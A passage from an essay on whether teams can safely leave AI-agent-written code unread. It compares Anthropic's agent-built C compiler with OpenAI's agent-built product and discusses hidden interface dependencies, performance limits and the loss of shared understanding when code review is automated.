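| | Anthropic's compiler | OpenAI's product |
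|---|---|---|
| Size | 100,000 lines | About a million lines |
| Effort | One researcher and 16 agents, over two weeks | Three engineers at first and later seven, over five months |
| What people specified | The goals and a few design choices | Tasks, acceptance criteria and rules about structure |
| What people read | Not reported | A sample of the code, mostly after merging |
| Main checks | Compiler test suites, real programs and comparison with an existing compiler | Tests, AI reviewers and enforced rules about structure |
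| What went wrong | New features often broke old ones | Agents copied poor patterns, and early users had performance problems |

The compiler passes 99% of most compiler test suites and can build a working Linux kernel for three kinds of processor. Carlini put most of the effort into tests and feedback for the agents. One of the best checks used GCC, an established compiler, as a reference. All 16 agents had been stuck on the same bug in the kernel, so Carlini compiled most of the kernel's files with GCC and a random selection with the new compiler. If the kernel then failed, the cause was among the files compiled with the new compiler, and an agent could narrow it down. Most new programs have no such reference to compare with.

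The compiler passed the tests but was not easy to extend, because new features and fixes frequently broke existing functions. Carlini tried hard to remove several limitations but did not fully succeed. He called the code's quality reasonable but nowhere near an expert's. Willison (2026) reports in *The Claude C Compiler* that the compiler expert Chris Lattner reviewed the code and was generally impressed.

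OpenAI's team relied more on structure. The code for each business area was divided into a fixed series of layers, from data types to the user interface, and dependencies between layers could run in only one direction. Automatic checks blocked any other dependency, but agents had considerable freedom within each layer. The agents still copied flawed patterns from elsewhere in the code, and at first the engineers spent every Friday cleaning up. The team then wrote its principles into the repository and had agents regularly look for violations and fix them.

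In the Latent Space interview *Extreme Harness Engineering for Token Billionaires*, Lopopolo compared the work to being technical lead of a 500-person organization, where nobody could read every change. Lopopolo reads a sample of the code to learn where the agents are struggling. People also decide when to prepare a release, and a person must approve a basic test of the application before the release goes out.

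Mistakes in this product matter less than they would in a public service, since its users were OpenAI staff and a few outside testers. The Wall Street Journal's *Vibe-Coded AI ‘Slop’ Is Flooding the World With Potentially Dangerous Code* reports that OpenAI's engineers remain responsible for reviewing AI-written code in critical infrastructure that serves millions of people. Lopopolo also says nobody yet knows how well the architecture of an agent-written system will hold up over years. Both accounts come from employees of companies that sell coding agents, and neither includes a defect rate.

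### Details that an interface leaves out

The case for leaving a module unread assumes that its interface covers everything other people and programs depend on. Hyrum's law, named after the software engineer Hyrum Wright, is that once an interface has enough users, somebody will depend on each of its observable behaviours, whatever the contract promises. Suppose the total has always been on the last line of each statement, and the accounts department uses a script that copies that line into a spreadsheet. If an agent then adds a thank-you message at the end, the Statements module still meets its contract, but the script copies the message instead of the total.

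Searching the program for calls to Statements would not have found this dependency, so it is hard to be sure that little else depends on a module. Comparing old and new statements would at least show the extra line, as a compatibility test would.

Speed, memory use and size can also affect other parts of a program. The programmer Joel Spolsky described this problem in his law of leaky abstractions, which holds that every non-trivial abstraction exposes some of the details it was meant to hide. For example, Carlini's compiler could produce correct code for the 16-bit mode in which some processors start up, but the result was over 60 kilobytes and Linux allows only 32. The agents couldn't make it small enough, so the compiler uses GCC for that step.

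Suppose an unread version of Statements in the customer program takes two seconds per customer. That would hardly matter for 100 customers, but 50,000 would take almost 28 hours. A contract can set a time limit, and a test can check it without anyone reading the code, but such checks cover only the limits that somebody thought to set. OpenAI's team gave its agents targets of this kind, such as starting a service in under 800 milliseconds.

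Modules that each work alone can also fail together, like the earlier pair that mixed up cents and dollars. Carlini's agents fixed the faults that showed up in individual kernel files, but some pairs of files still failed when the new compiler compiled both. Testing every pair would take a long time, since 1,000 files form 499,500 pairs. The customer program is easier to check because only Run calls the other modules, so a few end-to-end tests can cover the connections.

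Willison can no longer judge the quality of a project by looking at it, and would rather know that somebody has used it every day for two weeks than that it has good tests and documentation. Real use can expose problems that no contract covers, such as slow runs and broken spreadsheets. But by then the fault has already affected somebody, which may be acceptable if a statement is late but not if it goes to the wrong customer.

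### Who repairs unread code?

Reviewers learn how a program works by reading it. If they stop, there may be nobody who can repair it, especially when the person who submitted the code hasn't read it either. In the survey by Newman and colleagues, 49% of respondents said code authors were now less able to explain or justify a change, while 26% said the opposite. Most respondents (62%) said reviews felt less like mentoring, and 19% disagreed. They were more divided on whether review had become less useful for understanding the code base, with 43% agreeing and 38% disagreeing. One interviewee chose not to automate reviews fully because they were the main way to keep up with changes in the product.

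Engineering Enablement cites a Microsoft study in which only 14% of review comments concerned defects. It warns that automating review could lead to "cognitive debt", the researcher Margaret-Anne Storey's term for a growing gap between what a system does and what its team understands. The gap may not become obvious until an outage or a redesign. Adams and colleagues consider the loss of shared knowledge at Meta acceptable so far, because the changes RADAR handles differ from those people usually review. They acknowledge that this may not remain true as RADAR handles more changes.

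There is also some evidence that teams can work with code they haven't read. Tessl's *OpenAI's Framework for Shipping Code at 70 PRs/Week* (2026) reports that new engineers made Lopopolo's team faster within two weeks, which would be surprising if the code were impossible to work with. But the new engineers worked through agents, so this doesn't show that they could repair the program if the agents got stuck, as Carlini's agents did.

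None of these sources measured how long it takes to repair code that nobody has read. Researchers could test this directly by giving the same broken program to people who had reviewed it and people who had not, then comparing how quickly each group fixed it.

A team may not need to repair a module that meets the three conditions. An agent can instead rewrite Statements, for example, from its contract, and people can compare the new module's output with the worked examples and last month's statements. Somebody still has to know the charging rules well enough to decide which version is right when they differ. Replacing Records this way would be riskier, because every later step relies on what it returns, possibly including details that nobody wrote down.
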